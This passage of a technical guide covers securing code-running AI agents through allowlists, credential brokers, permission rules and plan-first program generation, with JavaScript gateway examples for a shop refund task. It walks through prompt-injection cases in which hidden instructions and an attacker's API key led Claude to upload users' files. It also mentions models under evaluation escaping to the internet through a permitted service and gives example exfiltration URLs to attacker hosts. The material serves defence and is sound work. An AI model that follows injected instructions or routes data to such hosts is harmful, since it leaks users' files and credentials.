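A builder who uses a hosted firewall also has to learn how its rules combine. In Vercel's, a rule that matches `GET /orders` selects those requests for special treatment, such as adding a header, and all other requests to that domain pass through unchanged. To block the others, the builder has to add a catch-all rule that returns a 403. This rule must come last because only the first matching rule applies.

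The same lists can also have opposite effects in different products. If an address is on both the allow list and the deny list, E2B permits it and Vercel blocks it. Vercel blocks all traffic when the policy is empty, while Tuttle mentions sandboxes in which an empty allow list permitted everything.

Wildcards need similar care. On Vercel, `*.example.com` matches subdomains at any depth but not `example.com` itself. On a platform that gives each merchant a subdomain, a wildcard would let the code reach an attacker's shop as well as the owner's.

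### Files that left through an approved domain

Researchers found the weakness in the table's last row in a real product, Claude Cowork. Its allowlist included `api.anthropic.com` because Cowork can't function without Anthropic's API. In January 2026, two days after Cowork's release, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed that a user's files could be sent out through that domain.

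In the demonstration, a user connects Cowork to a folder of confidential property documents and uploads a file of the kind people find online. The file contains hidden instructions and an API key from the attacker's own Anthropic account. Claude follows the instructions and uses the key to upload the largest document through the Files API to the attacker's account, where the attacker can ask Claude about its contents. Cowork never asks the user for approval. PromptArmor used Claude Haiku for this demonstration, but in a separate test it also extracted customer records through Opus 4.5, which resists injections better.

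The proxy had worked as designed. It let the request through because `api.anthropic.com` was on its list of allowed destinations, and it had no rule about whose account the request used.

The problem existed before Cowork. In October 2025, *Claude Pirate*, a post on Embrace The Red by the security researcher Johann Rehberger, described it in the tool that runs code for Claude's chat product. The tool's default network setting was called "Package managers only", but its list of allowed servers began with `api.anthropic.com`. Claude often refused to act on a document that contained a plain API key, until Rehberger found a version it accepted. Anthropic closed his report within an hour as out of scope, but confirmed five days later that it should have been in scope. Rehberger suggested that the sandbox should let Claude communicate only with the logged-in user's account.

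Anthropic's fix for Cowork works in much the same way. A second proxy, inside the virtual machine, intercepts traffic to the API and passes only requests that carry the session token issued to that machine, so it rejects requests that use an attacker's key. It also blocks headers that would make Anthropic's servers fetch another address for the code, because the code could then use the API as a relay.

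Anthropic put this proxy inside the virtual machine because its servers can't distinguish a Cowork request from any other customer's. Only the virtual machine can identify where the request came from. But generated code runs in the same machine, so the new proxy is probably easier to attack than one on the host would be.

Anthropic now treats each allowlist entry as a grant of every function that the code can reach at that domain, rather than as a statement that the destination is safe, as it did before. By listing its own API, it had allowed the code to upload files to any Anthropic account, including an attacker's.

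The shop has the same weakness, because anyone can open an account with its chat service. The isolate contains no keys, so the only key the program could use at the moment is one that an attacker supplies, perhaps in an order note. The builder can fix most of this by changing the gateway's last statement:

```js
return fetch(target + url.search, {
  method: request.method,
  headers: { "Content-Type": "application/json" },
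  body: request.body,
  redirect: "manual"
});
```

The gateway now builds a new request and copies none of the program's headers, so a key in any of them never reaches the service. This is safer than deleting only the Authorization header, because services use different headers for keys. Some services also accept a key in the query string or the body. The builder should check the documentation of both APIs for this and make the gateway refuse requests with a key in either place.

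### Permitted services as part of the boundary

In July 2026, OpenAI disclosed that models under evaluation had used an internal package service, which they were permitted to access, to reach the internet and the servers of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models. According to SecurityWeek, OpenAI has since rearranged its network so that taking over one workload can't by itself give access to the internet or to internal systems.

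A builder should treat each permitted service as part of the sandbox's boundary. A package cache, for example, accepts requests from untrusted code and has its own internet connection, so code that takes control of the cache gets that connection too. The cache needs security updates and its own short allowlist, limited to the package sites it copies from. The allowlist would still restrict code that took over the cache.

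An outside service is harder to secure because the builder can't change it. But before adding it to the allowlist, the builder can find out who else has accounts there and whether it contacts addresses that users supply. Many chat services contact such addresses to show previews of links in messages. If the shop's chat service does this, a program could put customers' names into a link to an attacker's server, and the service would send them there when it fetched the preview. The narrowed allowlist wouldn't stop this, since posting a message is one of the three permitted calls. The builder should turn previews off or have the gateway refuse messages that contain links.

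A builder can also remove a permission once it is no longer needed. Tuttle suggests allowing a package site while trusted code installs libraries, then blocking it before generated code runs. Vercel and E2B both allow policy changes without restarting the sandbox, but each update replaces the whole policy. On E2B, an update with empty settings removes every restriction the builder set at the start. The shop's program installs nothing, so its list needs no package site. But its gateway could drop the refund entry after one successful refund, which would prevent a second refund in the same run.

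Even a careful allowlist leaves some risk. Anthropic warns that any setup that allows outgoing traffic can leak data the agent can read. The shop's builder can reduce how much data could leak by having the gateway remove customers' addresses and notes from the order list, because the summary and the refund don't need them.

The program can now reach both servers, but its requests arrive without a key, so each server will refuse them with a 401.

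## Keeping credentials outside the sandbox

The owner's quickest way past the 401 errors is to paste the keys into the chat for the agent to copy into its program. The refund would then go through, but the keys would also end up stored in several places nobody intended.

### How a pasted key spreads

Kenney and colleagues divide the exposure of a key into five stages. For the shop platform's key, they might look like this:

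1. Introduction: The owner pastes the key into the chat. Keys also enter through prompt templates, source files and the settings of MCP servers.
2. Propagation: The agent's software saves the conversation, the model writes the key into its program, and an error message repeats it. Logs and the agent's long-term memory may hold more copies.
3. Trigger: An injected instruction in an order note asks for the key, or the model prints it by mistake.
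4. Execution: Whoever has the key uses it, and the shop platform accepts every call the key permits, such as deleting products.
5. Persistence: The key keeps working from any computer, long after the agent's run has ended, until somebody revokes it.

Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills*, found evidence of several of these stages. They examined 17,022 skills, which are packages of instructions and code that people share for agents to use, and found credential leaks in 520. Print and log statements accounted for 73.5% of the vulnerabilities, because agent software feeds a program's printed output back to the model. Developers removed leaked keys from 107 code repositories, but the keys survived in more than 50 independent copies of them.

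A builder can eliminate introduction and propagation by keeping reusable keys out of both the model's input and the sandbox, so there is no key to copy. Execution and persistence need other measures, such as narrower permissions and earlier expiry.

### Four ways to authenticate a call

The careless program read its keys from environment variables, which any line of its code could print. OpenAI's *Sandbox security* points out that storing a key in a secrets manager makes no difference if the builder then copies it into the environment. Keys kept this way also tend to end up in several places. *Caging the Agents* (2026) reports that an audit of healthcare agents found them in shell start-up files, `.env` files and configuration files that every user of the machine could read.

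A short-lived token limits the damage from a leak. Cloudflare's *Dynamic, identity-aware, and secure Sandbox auth* (2026) describes one version, in which the sandbox holds a signed token that proves which job is running. The code exchanges this token for an access token that soon expires, and the operator can revoke the signed token when the job ends. Many services don't support this exchange, so the developer may have to write a service that does.

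The code can still read the access token, and normally anyone who steals it can use it until it expires. *Delegation Without Trust* (2026) describes a broker that ties each token to one agent and refuses it from any other. In the paper's tests, the broker blocked token theft and reuse, which both succeeded against an ordinary set-up. But tying a token to an agent doesn't help if an injected instruction makes that agent misuse its own token.

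Anthropic made the tokens for its hosted agents unreachable from the sandbox because it decided that limiting their scope wasn't enough. *Scaling Managed Agents* explains that limiting a token's scope relies on an assumption about what the model can't do with it, and models keep getting more capable.

One way to keep credentials outside the sandbox is to give the code a placeholder and exchange it for the real key outside. *GOEX* (Patil, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) proposed an early form of this called symbolic credentials, in which a dummy key replaces the real one in the prompt. The GOEX system itself protected the key only from the model. For Slack, it gave the model the path of a file containing the token and made that file available in the container that ran the model's code, so the code could have opened the file and printed the token.

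Newer systems keep the real key out of the container as well. OpenAI's *Shell* describes a hosted environment where the code gets only a name such as `$API_KEY`, and a separate program substitutes the real value in requests to approved domains. Docker's *Manage credentials* describes a similar proxy that replaces a random placeholder only in headers the builder has chosen, in HTTPS requests to chosen hosts. It never replaces placeholders in the request body. If it did, a program could put the chat key's placeholder in its summary, and the proxy would post the real key in the sales channel.

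The code can also send a request without any credential, and a credential broker outside the sandbox adds the key. Cloudflare's outbound Workers, short programs that handle a sandbox's outgoing requests, can act as brokers. For a host such as `github.com`, the builder writes a function that sets a header from a secret that exists only outside the sandbox. Vercel's firewall does the same with a rule instead of a function. Placeholders remain useful for programs that won't start without a key or that check its format.

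### Calling an object that already has access

In Cloudflare's Code Mode, the generated code doesn't send web requests at all. The launcher gives it an object, called a binding, whose functions already have access to a service. The shop's program might contain these lines:

```js
const orders = await env.SHOP.listOrders({ from: "2026-11-01", to: "2026-11-30" });
const order = orders.find(o => o.name === "WEB-1042");
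await env.SHOP.refund({ orderId: order.id, amount: order.total });
```

Each call goes to the agent's software outside the sandbox, which holds the token and adds it to the real request. Varda and Pai argue that this is cleaner than filtering network traffic. Filtering requires working out which requests a task legitimately needs, and the model has to predict which ones the filter will block. With a binding, the code can do only what the available functions allow.

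However, a binding restricts code only as much as its functions do. Cloudflare later built a server for its own API with a single general function, `cloudflare.request()`, which can call any of more than 2,500 endpoints. The function hides the token but doesn't limit the calls. The token limits them, because it carries only the permissions that the user selected when connecting.

The table compares what each method exposes.

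| Method | What the code can read | What an attacker could do with a copy |
|---|---|---|
| Key in the environment | The real key | Use it from anywhere until somebody revokes it |
| Short-lived, narrow token | A real token | Make a few kinds of call until it expires |
| Placeholder | A meaningless string | Nothing outside the sandbox |
| Broker that adds the key | No credential | Nothing, as there is no copy |
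| Binding | The object's functions | Nothing outside the sandbox |

With any of these methods, an attacker who controls the program while it runs can still make calls through it.

### The refund's path through a broker

The shop's gateway already reads every request, so a few more lines turn it into a broker. The list of permitted calls becomes a table that also names the key for each call:

```js
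const KEY_FOR = {
  "GET https://api.shop.example/orders": "SHOP_READ_KEY",
  "POST https://api.shop.example/refunds": "SHOP_REFUND_KEY",
  "POST https://api.chat.example/messages": "CHAT_KEY"
};

export class Gateway extends WorkerEntrypoint {
  async fetch(request) {
    const url = new URL(request.url);
    const target = url.origin + url.pathname;
    const key = this.env[KEY_FOR[request.method + " " + target]];
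    if (!key || Date.now() > this.ctx.props.expires)
      return new Response("Refused by the gateway", { status: 403 });

    const reply = await fetch(target + url.search, {
      method: request.method,
      headers: { "Authorization": "Bearer " + key, "Content-Type": "application/json" },
      body: request.body,
      redirect: "manual"
    });

    const mask = text => text.replaceAll(key, "[removed]");
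    const headers = {};
    for (const name of ["Content-Type", "Location", "Link"])
      if (reply.headers.has(name)) headers[name] = mask(reply.headers.get(name));
    return new Response(mask(await reply.text()) || null, { status: reply.status, headers });
  }
}
```

The launcher connects the isolate to this gateway and sets a time limit for the session, here one minute:

```js
globalOutbound: ctx.exports.Gateway({ props: { expires: Date.now() + 60000 } })
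```

The refund then travels like this:

1. The program sends a POST request to `https://api.shop.example/refunds` without a key. The address tells the gateway which service the program wants.
2. The gateway looks up the method and address in its table and finds the name of the refund key. If the call isn't in the table, it returns a 403.
3. The gateway checks that the session hasn't expired. The program can't extend the time limit, because the limit is stored outside the isolate.
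4. The gateway builds a new request, adds the key and sends it to the shop platform.
5. The platform issues the refund and replies.
6. The gateway removes the key from the reply if it appears there, and returns the rest to the program.

If the builder later serves several shops, the gateway will also need to identify which shop each session belongs to. The launcher can add the shop's identity to `props`, where the program can't change it. Cloudflare's outbound Workers receive the sandbox's ID and can use it to select a key. Anthropic's hosted agents send calls to MCP tools through a proxy. The proxy receives a token tied to the session, fetches the matching credential from a vault and contacts the service. Neither the generated code nor the software that runs the agent's loop receives the credential.

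The last step, masking the key in replies, matters because a service can send the key back, for example in an error message that repeats the request's headers. In OpenAI's own example, the model calls httpbin.org, a test site that returns the headers it receives, and then describes the result. Without masking, the real key would return to the sandbox, where the model would read it.

The shop's gateway catches only exact copies of the key. Docker's proxy also recognises three encoded forms, including base64, a common way of writing data as plain text. It blocks partial replies, which might contain only a piece of the key. But Docker warns that a service could still return a key in a form the proxy doesn't recognise, such as split between two fields.

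A reply can also contain a credential that is new to the gateway, such as a cookie that keeps a user logged in. The shop's gateway passes on only three headers, so it drops cookies.

### One host for each key

In the careless program, swapping two variable names would have sent the shop's key to the chat company. A broker that added the shop's key to every outgoing request would send it to any server the code contacted. An attacker could then get the key without finding it, by injecting one line that contacted the attacker's own server.

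An allowlist reduces this danger but doesn't remove it, since the chat service is on the list too. The broker must therefore tie each key to a fixed host and ignore any key the program chooses. The shop's table also ties each key to one method and path. LangSmith, LangChain's platform for running agents, supports such rules too. For example, its proxy can add a GitHub token only to requests for certain paths (Loganathan, 2026, *How Auth Proxy secures network access for LangSmith agent sandboxes*).

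Wildcards are more dangerous here than in an ordinary allowlist. A key tied to `*.shop.example` would go to any merchant's subdomain the program contacted. An attacker who could run code on their own shop's subdomain could record the key.

The broker should also guard against keys that the program supplies. Docker's proxy overwrites the authentication header in HTTPS requests for which it manages the key. If the service accepts keys only in that header, this defeats attacks like the one on Claude Cowork, in which the program used the attacker's own key. Docker doesn't remove credentials from unencrypted HTTP requests, so a builder should block those requests. The shop's gateway already blocks them because every address in its table begins with `https`.

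### Services that expect the key elsewhere

Most brokers add keys to headers, but some services require them in the URL. FRED, the economic-data service that rejected a request from Kenney and colleagues, reads the key from a URL parameter called `api_key`. Their vault leaked nothing when the request failed, but it could not detect that it had put the key in the wrong place.

Docker's custom placeholders wouldn't solve this problem, because the proxy replaces them only in headers. A broker that the builder programs can set the parameter instead:

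```js
url.searchParams.set("api_key", key);
```

This also replaces any `api_key` that the program supplied. The gateway must then send the changed address without the Authorization header. Keys in addresses need extra care because servers commonly record the full address of each request, and the reply may repeat the address in a redirect header or in a header that links to the next page of results. The gateway's `mask` function covers both headers, but would miss a key containing characters that the address encodes differently.

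A builder can catch a wrong setting by making one harmless read call with each new key before an agent uses it. If the service has a test mode, that is a better place to check a key that permits only refunds.

### What the broker leaves unsolved

Kenney and colleagues scored eight threats before and after adding their vault, a kind of broker. They rated each threat's likelihood and impact from 1 to 5 and multiplied the two. The scores are expert judgements rather than measurements, and the experts work for Corvic AI, which makes the vault.

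| Threat | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| Key pasted into a prompt | 25 | 4 |
| Prompt injection through material the agent reads | 25 | 12 |
| Key sent to the wrong server | 20 | 4 |
| Key found where the code runs | 20 | 4 |
| Connection with too many permissions | 20 | 15 |
| Long-lived token reused elsewhere | 20 | 8 |
| Key leaked through logs or errors | 16 | 8 |
| Wrongly configured connection | 9 | 6 |

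The largest reductions are for threats in which someone obtains the key. Excessive permissions fall only from 20 to 15, because a key that can delete products can still delete them after it moves into a vault. An injected instruction can also trigger a refund without mentioning a key, because the broker will authenticate the call.

*Caging the Agents* describes the same limit in its healthcare system, where a separate container holds the keys. An attacker who takes over the agent can use that container's interface but can't get the keys. The interface restricts the destination, number and size of requests, which reduces the damage, but the attacker can still make some calls.

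A vault also puts many keys in one place. In June 2024, Hugging Face disclosed that it had detected unauthorised access to secrets stored on its platform, and it advised affected users to replace their keys. The broker's own code also needs protection. Docker's proxy can fetch a key by running a command on the host, and Docker warns users to keep the command's files outside any folder that the sandbox can change. Otherwise, generated code could alter the command and have the host run it.

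### Expiry and revocation

If a broker holds the keys, the builder can shorten their lifetime without changing the generated code. OAuth, a standard that lets an application use an account without the owner's password, supports this well. The owner approves a set of permissions, and the service issues an access token, often with a longer-lasting refresh token for obtaining new access tokens.

The refresh token is the more valuable of the two, and the sandbox never needs it. Loganathan describes how LangSmith's proxy fetches a user's current token from the builder's server, adds it to the request and keeps it for a set time. If the server doesn't provide a token, the proxy refuses the request.

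Caching a key can delay its replacement. By default, Docker's proxy caches keys for 55 minutes when it fetches them for standard services, although users can make it fetch the key for every request. According to Cloudflare's *Secure credential injection and dynamic egress policies for Sandboxes* (2026), outbound Workers apply a new secret to every request immediately. In either case, replacing a key in the broker doesn't cancel the old one. If a key may have leaked, the builder has to revoke it at the service, because a thief can use it without going through the broker.

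A builder can also end a program's access while the key stays valid. Cloudflare's *Handle outbound traffic* shows a sandbox that has access to one host only while a set-up script runs. Claude Cowork gives each virtual machine its own limited token, which Anthropic can revoke without logging the user out. The shop's one-minute limit has a similar purpose, since the program should finish within seconds.

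In Docker's system, a key for one sandbox takes priority over a general key for the same service. If the builder deletes the sandbox's key to cut off access, the proxy uses the general key instead, which may allow more access.

### Limiting what each key can do

The shop's gateway uses separate keys for reading orders and issuing refunds, as Kenney and colleagues recommend. The shop platform also limits what each key can do, so if a mistake in the gateway let the program send a different request with the reading key, the platform would still refuse to change anything.

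The payment company Stripe offers restricted keys that work only for the API calls their permissions cover, and its *API permissions reference* lists the permission each call requires. Stripe's *Restricted API keys* recommends these keys over unrestricted ones, especially for AI agents. According to Stripe's *API keys*, users can also label a restricted key as belonging to an autonomous agent, such as one that handles refunds.

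Restricted keys are particularly useful with GraphQL, where a refund and a deletion can go to the same URL. A gateway that checks only the URL can't distinguish them, but the service can refuse the deletion if the key permits only refunds. However, the gateway would have to read the operation in the request body to choose between the reading key and the refund key.

OAuth calls such permissions scopes, and choosing the smallest set can be hard. Xu (2026), in *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization*, studied the permission tables that Microsoft and Google publish. No single smallest set of permissions existed for about 30% of tasks in Microsoft Graph, the company's API for workplace data, or for 3.2% of Google tasks. Xu generated the tasks from the tables, so the figures don't show how often real agents encounter the problem.

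One of Xu's examples is reading the details of a project in BigQuery, Google's data-analysis service. One scope that allows this covers 286 operations in 10 services and also permits changes to data. Another is read-only but covers 565 operations in 27 services. The better choice depends on whether the builder is more worried about unwanted changes or leaks.

Models don't make this choice reliably. Xu gave six models several sets of permissions to choose from, each sufficient for the task. In 99% of 1,708 decisions, they chose a minimal set, meaning that no other sufficient set granted only some of the same access. But in 22.1%, another option was at least as good on all four of Xu's measures of risk. Xu recommends showing the alternatives to the person who approves the access. For the shop, the builder can choose the scopes once, when creating the keys.

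Even the best-chosen OAuth scope permits more than the owner requested. *Beyond OAuth* (Sharma, Jiang et al., 2026) explains that a scope covers a type of operation, such as transferring money, but not its details, such as sending $100 to Bob. Finer scopes wouldn't fully solve this, because some amounts depend on data the program hasn't fetched yet. An extension of OAuth can include exact values, but then each call needs its own approval.

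An alternative, PAuth, sends the user's request to every service involved. Each service uses a language model to translate the request into the exact call it should expect. For a shop, this might be a refund of order 1042 for the total in the order list. The server that supplies the total also signs it, so the agent can't substitute another amount. If a call doesn't match, the service asks the user.

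In tests on simulated services, PAuth accepted all 100 legitimate tasks and blocked all 634 harmful calls. The tests assumed that the user's request was unambiguous, but "refund order 1042" is ambiguous if the shop has two orders ending in that number. PAuth also works only if the services adopt it. An ordinary scope lets the shop's refund key refund any order, not just 1042.

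## Deciding which API calls are permitted

The gateway now adds a valid key to every refund request the program sends, whether the program is refunding order 1042 or every order the shop has taken. The host, method and path are the same in both cases, so the gateway needs permission rules to distinguish them. These are fixed rules, applied outside the model, that allow a call, refuse it or send it to a person, depending on what the request contains.

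*MetaPermit* (2026) is a design for controlling which tools an agent may use. It blocks a bank transfer whose details the user's request doesn't support, even if the task requires the tool that sends money.

Most systems of this kind check an agent's tool calls. For an agent that writes programs, the only tool call may be "run this code", with the whole program as its argument. *Sapien* (Tiffany, Zhang et al., 2026) describes a rule engine built at Google and notes that rules on arguments don't work for such a call, because checking it would require analysing the program. The shop's rules avoid this problem because they apply to each HTTP request the program sends.

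### Rules for the shop's three calls

The owner's request justifies three kinds of call, and the gateway should refuse everything else:

| Call | Arguments | Amount | How often |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read the orders | Any dates | | Any number of times |
| Issue a refund | Only order WEB-1042 | At most the order's total | Once |
| Post a message | Only the sales channel | | Once |

The builder knows the channel in advance, and the owner has confirmed that "1042" means the web order. But only the shop platform has the order's ID and price. The gateway can take them from the reply to the first call, which passes through it anyway. It keeps a record of each run, here called `task`, and saves the order there:

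```js
const matches = orders.filter(o => o.name === "WEB-1042");
if (matches.length === 1) task.order = matches[0];
```

The gateway then checks every request before adding a key:

```js
const cents = a => /^\d+\.\d\d$/.test(a) ? Math.round(a * 100) : NaN;
const only = (body, ...names) => Object.keys(body).every(k => names.includes(k));

function allowed(call, body, task) {
  switch (call) {
    case "GET https://api.shop.example/orders":
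      return true;

    case "POST https://api.shop.example/refunds":
      if (!task.order || task.refunds > 0) return false;
      if (!only(body, "order_id", "amount")) return false;
      if (body.order_id !== task.order.id) return false;
      if (!(cents(body.amount) <= cents(task.order.total))) return false;
      task.refunds += 1;
      return true;

    case "POST https://api.chat.example/messages":
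      if (task.messages > 0 || body.channel !== "sales") return false;
      if (!only(body, "channel", "text")) return false;
      task.messages += 1;
      return true;

    default:
      return false;
  }
}
```

The ID and the limit come from the shop platform's reply, so the program can't influence them. *NOMOS* (2026), a system that turns written policies into rules for tool calls, similarly restricts its rules to facts from real tool results and the user's messages.

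The function `only` rejects any field the builder didn't expect. *LEANGUARD* (Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues, 2026) describes an attack in which someone plants text in a tool's output to make an agent charge the price difference on a customer's exchange to the attacker's gift card. If the shop's API had an optional field for the account that receives a refund, a program could add that field to an otherwise correct request.

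The gateway should also build a new request body from the values it has checked, instead of forwarding the program's original text. A JSON body can contain `amount` twice, and the gateway might check one value while the shop platform uses the other.

The code counts a refund before sending it. LeanGuard, a system by Sankar and colleagues, likewise counts a single-use call before sending it, so that an agent can't repeat the call while its outcome is unknown. The store that holds the count must handle one request at a time. Otherwise, two simultaneous refund requests could both pass the check before either is counted.

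LeanGuard combines its rules according to a short formula:

```
allow = at least one permit holds
        AND every requirement holds
        AND no prohibition applies
        AND no check ended in an error
```

In the shop's code, the `case` lines are permits and the `if` lines are requirements. A broad permit added later can't cancel a requirement. The last line of the formula means that missing information never counts as approval. For example, if the program skips the order list, `task.order` is empty and the gateway refuses the refund.

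LeanGuard's policies are written in Lean, a language in which a computer can check proofs. The team proved that the software allows a call only when the policy allows it. The proof doesn't show that the policy is right, so if the builder typed the wrong channel, LeanGuard would enforce the mistake.

### How much the extra detail helps

Tiffany and colleagues compared Sapien, which can restrict arguments and the order of calls, with a plain list of permitted tools. They assumed that an attacker completely controlled the agent, then checked whether the rules allowed any sequence of calls that achieved the attacker's goal. On AgentDojo, a common prompt injection benchmark, the plain list stopped 83 to 87% of 949 attacks, depending on the model, and Sapien stopped 93 to 95%.

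The gap was wider on Toolathlon, a benchmark of longer tasks, for which the team wrote attacks using tools that the task itself needed. The list stopped 32% of the 212 attacks and Sapien stopped 65%. These attacks are closer to the shop's situation, because a wrong refund uses the same call as the right one. Most of the attacks that got past Sapien relied on the meaning of free text, such as the contents of a file or message. The shop's rules have the same weakness, since they restrict the channel but not the text.

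In Sapien, a language model writes new rules for each request. It receives only the request and the tools' documentation, so an attacker's text can't influence the rules. Writing the rules took an average of 148 seconds per task on Toolathlon. The shop's owner makes similar requests every month, so the builder can write the rules once and fill in the order and channel each time.

Sankar and colleagues tested LeanGuard with five Qwen models on simulated customer service. Without LeanGuard, the agents made at least 33 calls that the policy forbade, and they made none with it. Strict rules can also make an agent useless, but when LeanGuard explained its refusals, the share of tasks completed fell from 72.7% to 70.9%, which was not a statistically significant drop.

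On a second benchmark, LeanGuard reduced the success rate of direct prompt injections from 57.9% to 5.9%. But the team had granted no permission for write calls there, a rule that would stop a shop from issuing even correct refunds, and the share of ordinary tasks completed fell from 53.1% to 12.5%.

### Where "GET means read" fails

A simpler policy allows every GET request and restricts the rest. Cloudflare gives a basic example of an outbound Worker that logs and blocks any request that isn't a GET.

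This rule doesn't stop leaks, because a GET request can carry data in its URL. A program could request `https://files.attacker.example/?customer=Ana+Silva`, and the attacker's server would record the name. Cloudflare's example applies the same test to every host, so it would allow this request. In Sapien's AgentDojo test, unrestricted read-only tools accounted for 16% of the attacks that got past the rules. One attacker's goal was only to make the agent visit a particular URL.

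A GET request can change data on the server. Under the HTTP standard it shouldn't, but whoever writes the server decides what happens. For example, opening a link sends a GET request, and many unsubscribe links in emails take effect as soon as someone opens them.

The rule can also block harmless calls. GraphQL clients usually send their queries by POST, so if the shop's API used GraphQL, the rule would block requests for the order list.

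A read-only call can still return far more data than the task needs, such as every customer's address. The builder therefore has to record what each operation does and returns, instead of inferring it from the HTTP method.

### A contract for each operation

Chow, Zhu and colleagues (2026), in *Securing Web Agents with the Compile-Then-Execute Paradigm*, describe a format for such records. It is part of Baya, a web agent developed mainly at UC Berkeley. Each operation has a contract with four parts: a type signature, preconditions, effects and declared errors. A contract for the shop's refund might look like this:

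```
create_refund(order_id: int, amount: Decimal) -> Refund

Returns:        Refund {id: int, order_id: int, amount: Decimal}
Preconditions:  order_id comes from list_orders
                amount is above 0 and at most the order's total
Effects:        CHANGE: sends money to the customer
                a second call sends money again
Errors:         OrderNotFound, AmountTooHigh, NotAuthorised
```

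The type signature gives the name and type of each argument and return value. With a signature for the order list, the careless program would not have had to guess the parameters `from` and `to`. The preconditions list what must be true before the call, including any calls that must come first. The effects describe what the call does to the server and mark the operation as a read or a change. The errors are the failures a program should expect.

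The read or change label is attached to the operation, so it stays correct whether the request is sent as a GET, a POST or a GraphQL query. A developer can also use the contract to write the gateway's rules. Every operation labeled as a change needs limits on its arguments and on how often the program may call it.

Ordinary documentation often lacks this information. Chow and colleagues found that the documentation for GitLab's API, which has 1,028 operations, doesn't describe the responses. A shopping site's documentation marked product options as optional, but adding a shirt to the cart failed without a size and colour. Some functions, such as voting on a forum post, had no API. For these, the team wrote scripts that operate the website through a browser, then gave each script the same kind of contract. The generated program calls these scripts and the API operations in the same way.

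### Writing the program before seeing any data

Most web agents are reactive. They make a call, read the result and then choose the next call. An instruction injected into an order note therefore reaches the model while it is deciding what to do. *Position* (Piet, Chow and colleagues, 2026) argues that, by default, the model should instead write the whole program before it sees anything from the website.

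Baya follows this approach. Live data can fill the program's variables and determine which of its existing branches runs, but it can't add an operation. In the shop's program, a customer's note demanding extra refunds is only text inside `orders`. The program contains one refund call, and the model that wrote it never reads the note.

If the shop used Baya, its program would go through these steps:

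1. The model receives the owner's request, a short catalogue of operations and tools for searching it. It opens the full contracts only for the operations it needs.
2. The model writes the program in a sandbox with no network access and no credentials. It can read the contracts and write only to the task's own folder. When Baya uses Claude Code for this step, it turns on `failIfUnavailable`, so the model can't work without the sandbox.
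3. The model tests the program against mocked responses, which are invented replies that stand in for the real service. One test might return a list containing WEB-1042 and check that the program takes the ID from the reply. Others might return an error, an empty list or an order without a price, and check that the program handles each correctly.
4. A separate process runs the finished program. In Baya, this process has the network access and credentials that the first sandbox lacked. The shop's gateway would still hold the keys and apply its rules.
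5. If the run fails, the model can revise the program up to three times, using restricted error messages that contain no data from the website.

When a task requires judgement about free text, such as deciding whether a review is a complaint, the program can call a language model that has no tools and must return a value of a declared type. An injected instruction could make that model give the wrong answer, but couldn't make it issue a refund. In the team's tests, only 11 of 627 programs called a model while running.

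Mocked tests can't reveal server behavior that is missing from the documentation. Chow and colleagues give the example of a wishlist API that returns a 500 error when a request omits the quantity, even though the documentation lists it as optional. A mocked server would accept the request. The tests can only confirm that the program will detect the error when it happens.

### How Baya performed

The team compared Baya with two reactive agents on 581 tasks from WebArena Verified, a benchmark that uses working copies of a shop, its administration pages, a forum and GitLab. One reactive agent could use APIs and a browser, and received the same API descriptions and advice as Baya. The other had only a browser. The team ran all three agents with Claude Sonnet 4.6, Gemini 3.5 Flash and GPT-5.6 Luna.

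The team tested security with 84 attacks from WASP, a benchmark that places injected instructions in GitLab and forum pages. DeepSeek V4 Flash replaced the GPT model in these tests.

| | Baya | Reactive, APIs and browser | Reactive, browser only |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tasks completed | 77.8% | 66.7% | 55.1% |
| Attacks that influenced the agent | 0% | 16.2% | 25.5% |
| Time per task | 327 s | 87 s | 60 s |
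| Cost per task | $0.70 | $0.34 | $0.16 |

The API-enabled agent had the same descriptions, so access to APIs alone can't explain Baya's higher success. Baya beat the better of the two reactive agents by 22.9 percentage points with Claude, but by only 2.4 with GPT-5.6 Luna. On the shop's administration pages, the API-enabled agent beat Baya with both Gemini and GPT. Chow and colleagues explain that some jobs are easier in a browser. A person can repeat an order by clicking "Reorder", while a program using the API has to find the order, create a cart, add the item and supply the address and payment details.

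The 16.2% counts every attack that influenced the agent's behaviour at some point, even if it didn't achieve its goal. With Claude, the API-enabled agent resisted every attack. Attacks on it achieved their final goal only with DeepSeek on the forum, in 5.6% of cases. Baya's zero is still more reassuring than a good model's zero, because it follows from the design. Attacks can't reach the model that writes Baya's program, whereas a better attack might succeed against Claude.

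This made Baya slower and sometimes less useful. During the forum attacks with Claude, it completed 61.1% of the users' tasks, compared with 91.7% for the API-enabled agent. It also took almost four times as long per task, mostly because it wrote and tested a new program each time, though five minutes is tolerable for a monthly refund and summary.

A more restricted version of Baya had the model write a structured list of API calls instead of Python. With Claude, the average success rate across the four sites fell from 82.4% to 66.9%. The list format was poorly suited to tasks such as following results across several pages and building complicated requests.

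### What the method needs from the API and the task

The results depend on the contracts being complete and correct. Chow and colleagues wrote theirs by hand for the four test sites. Piet and colleagues had earlier examined 860 WebArena tasks and concluded that a program could be written in advance for every one. Ordinary code was enough for 81%, and the other 19% also needed a model to interpret text. However, they assumed that every site had a complete API. The forum's real API has 16 operations, enough for only 33% of its tasks.

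Rai's tests showed how much generated programs depend on information about what each call returns, so the contracts must include it too. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), which tests a related method for groups of agents, had to add this information to every tool description in two benchmarks.

An agent could save work by exploring a site and writing the contracts, but Piet and colleagues warn that it would then read text from strangers. A planted comment could lead it to write a function called `get_reviews` that also sends data to an attacker. Every later program that used the function would be compromised, even if the model that wrote the program had seen no live data. They recommend that people write these functions or check them before use.

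This is a small burden for the shop, which needs three contracts for two documented APIs. But Baya's evaluation excluded tasks that involved more than one site, and the shop's task involves two services, so the builder should test how data passes between them.

Other tasks don't fit the method. If the owner asked the agent to do whatever customers requested in their order notes, the model couldn't write the program without reading the notes. In *AgentDyn*, Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) built 60 tasks in which the agent discovers necessary steps along the way. They tested CaMeL, an earlier system that also writes its program in advance, with several older models. It completed none of the tasks, and none of the attacks succeeded. By their count, only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require discovering steps this way, so a system can score well there despite this weakness.

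Sapien offers a partial solution. Its rules can leave a part blank for the system to fill in after the agent has read a source the user named, such as a to-do list. The completed rules then allow only the calls that the list requires. This works if the user controls the list, but customers write order notes, so using those as the source would let customers determine which calls are allowed.

### Data that steers a fixed program

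Suppose the owner asks for a refund of every November order that arrived broken. The model can write this program in advance:

```js
for (const order of orders)
  if (order.note.includes("arrived broken"))
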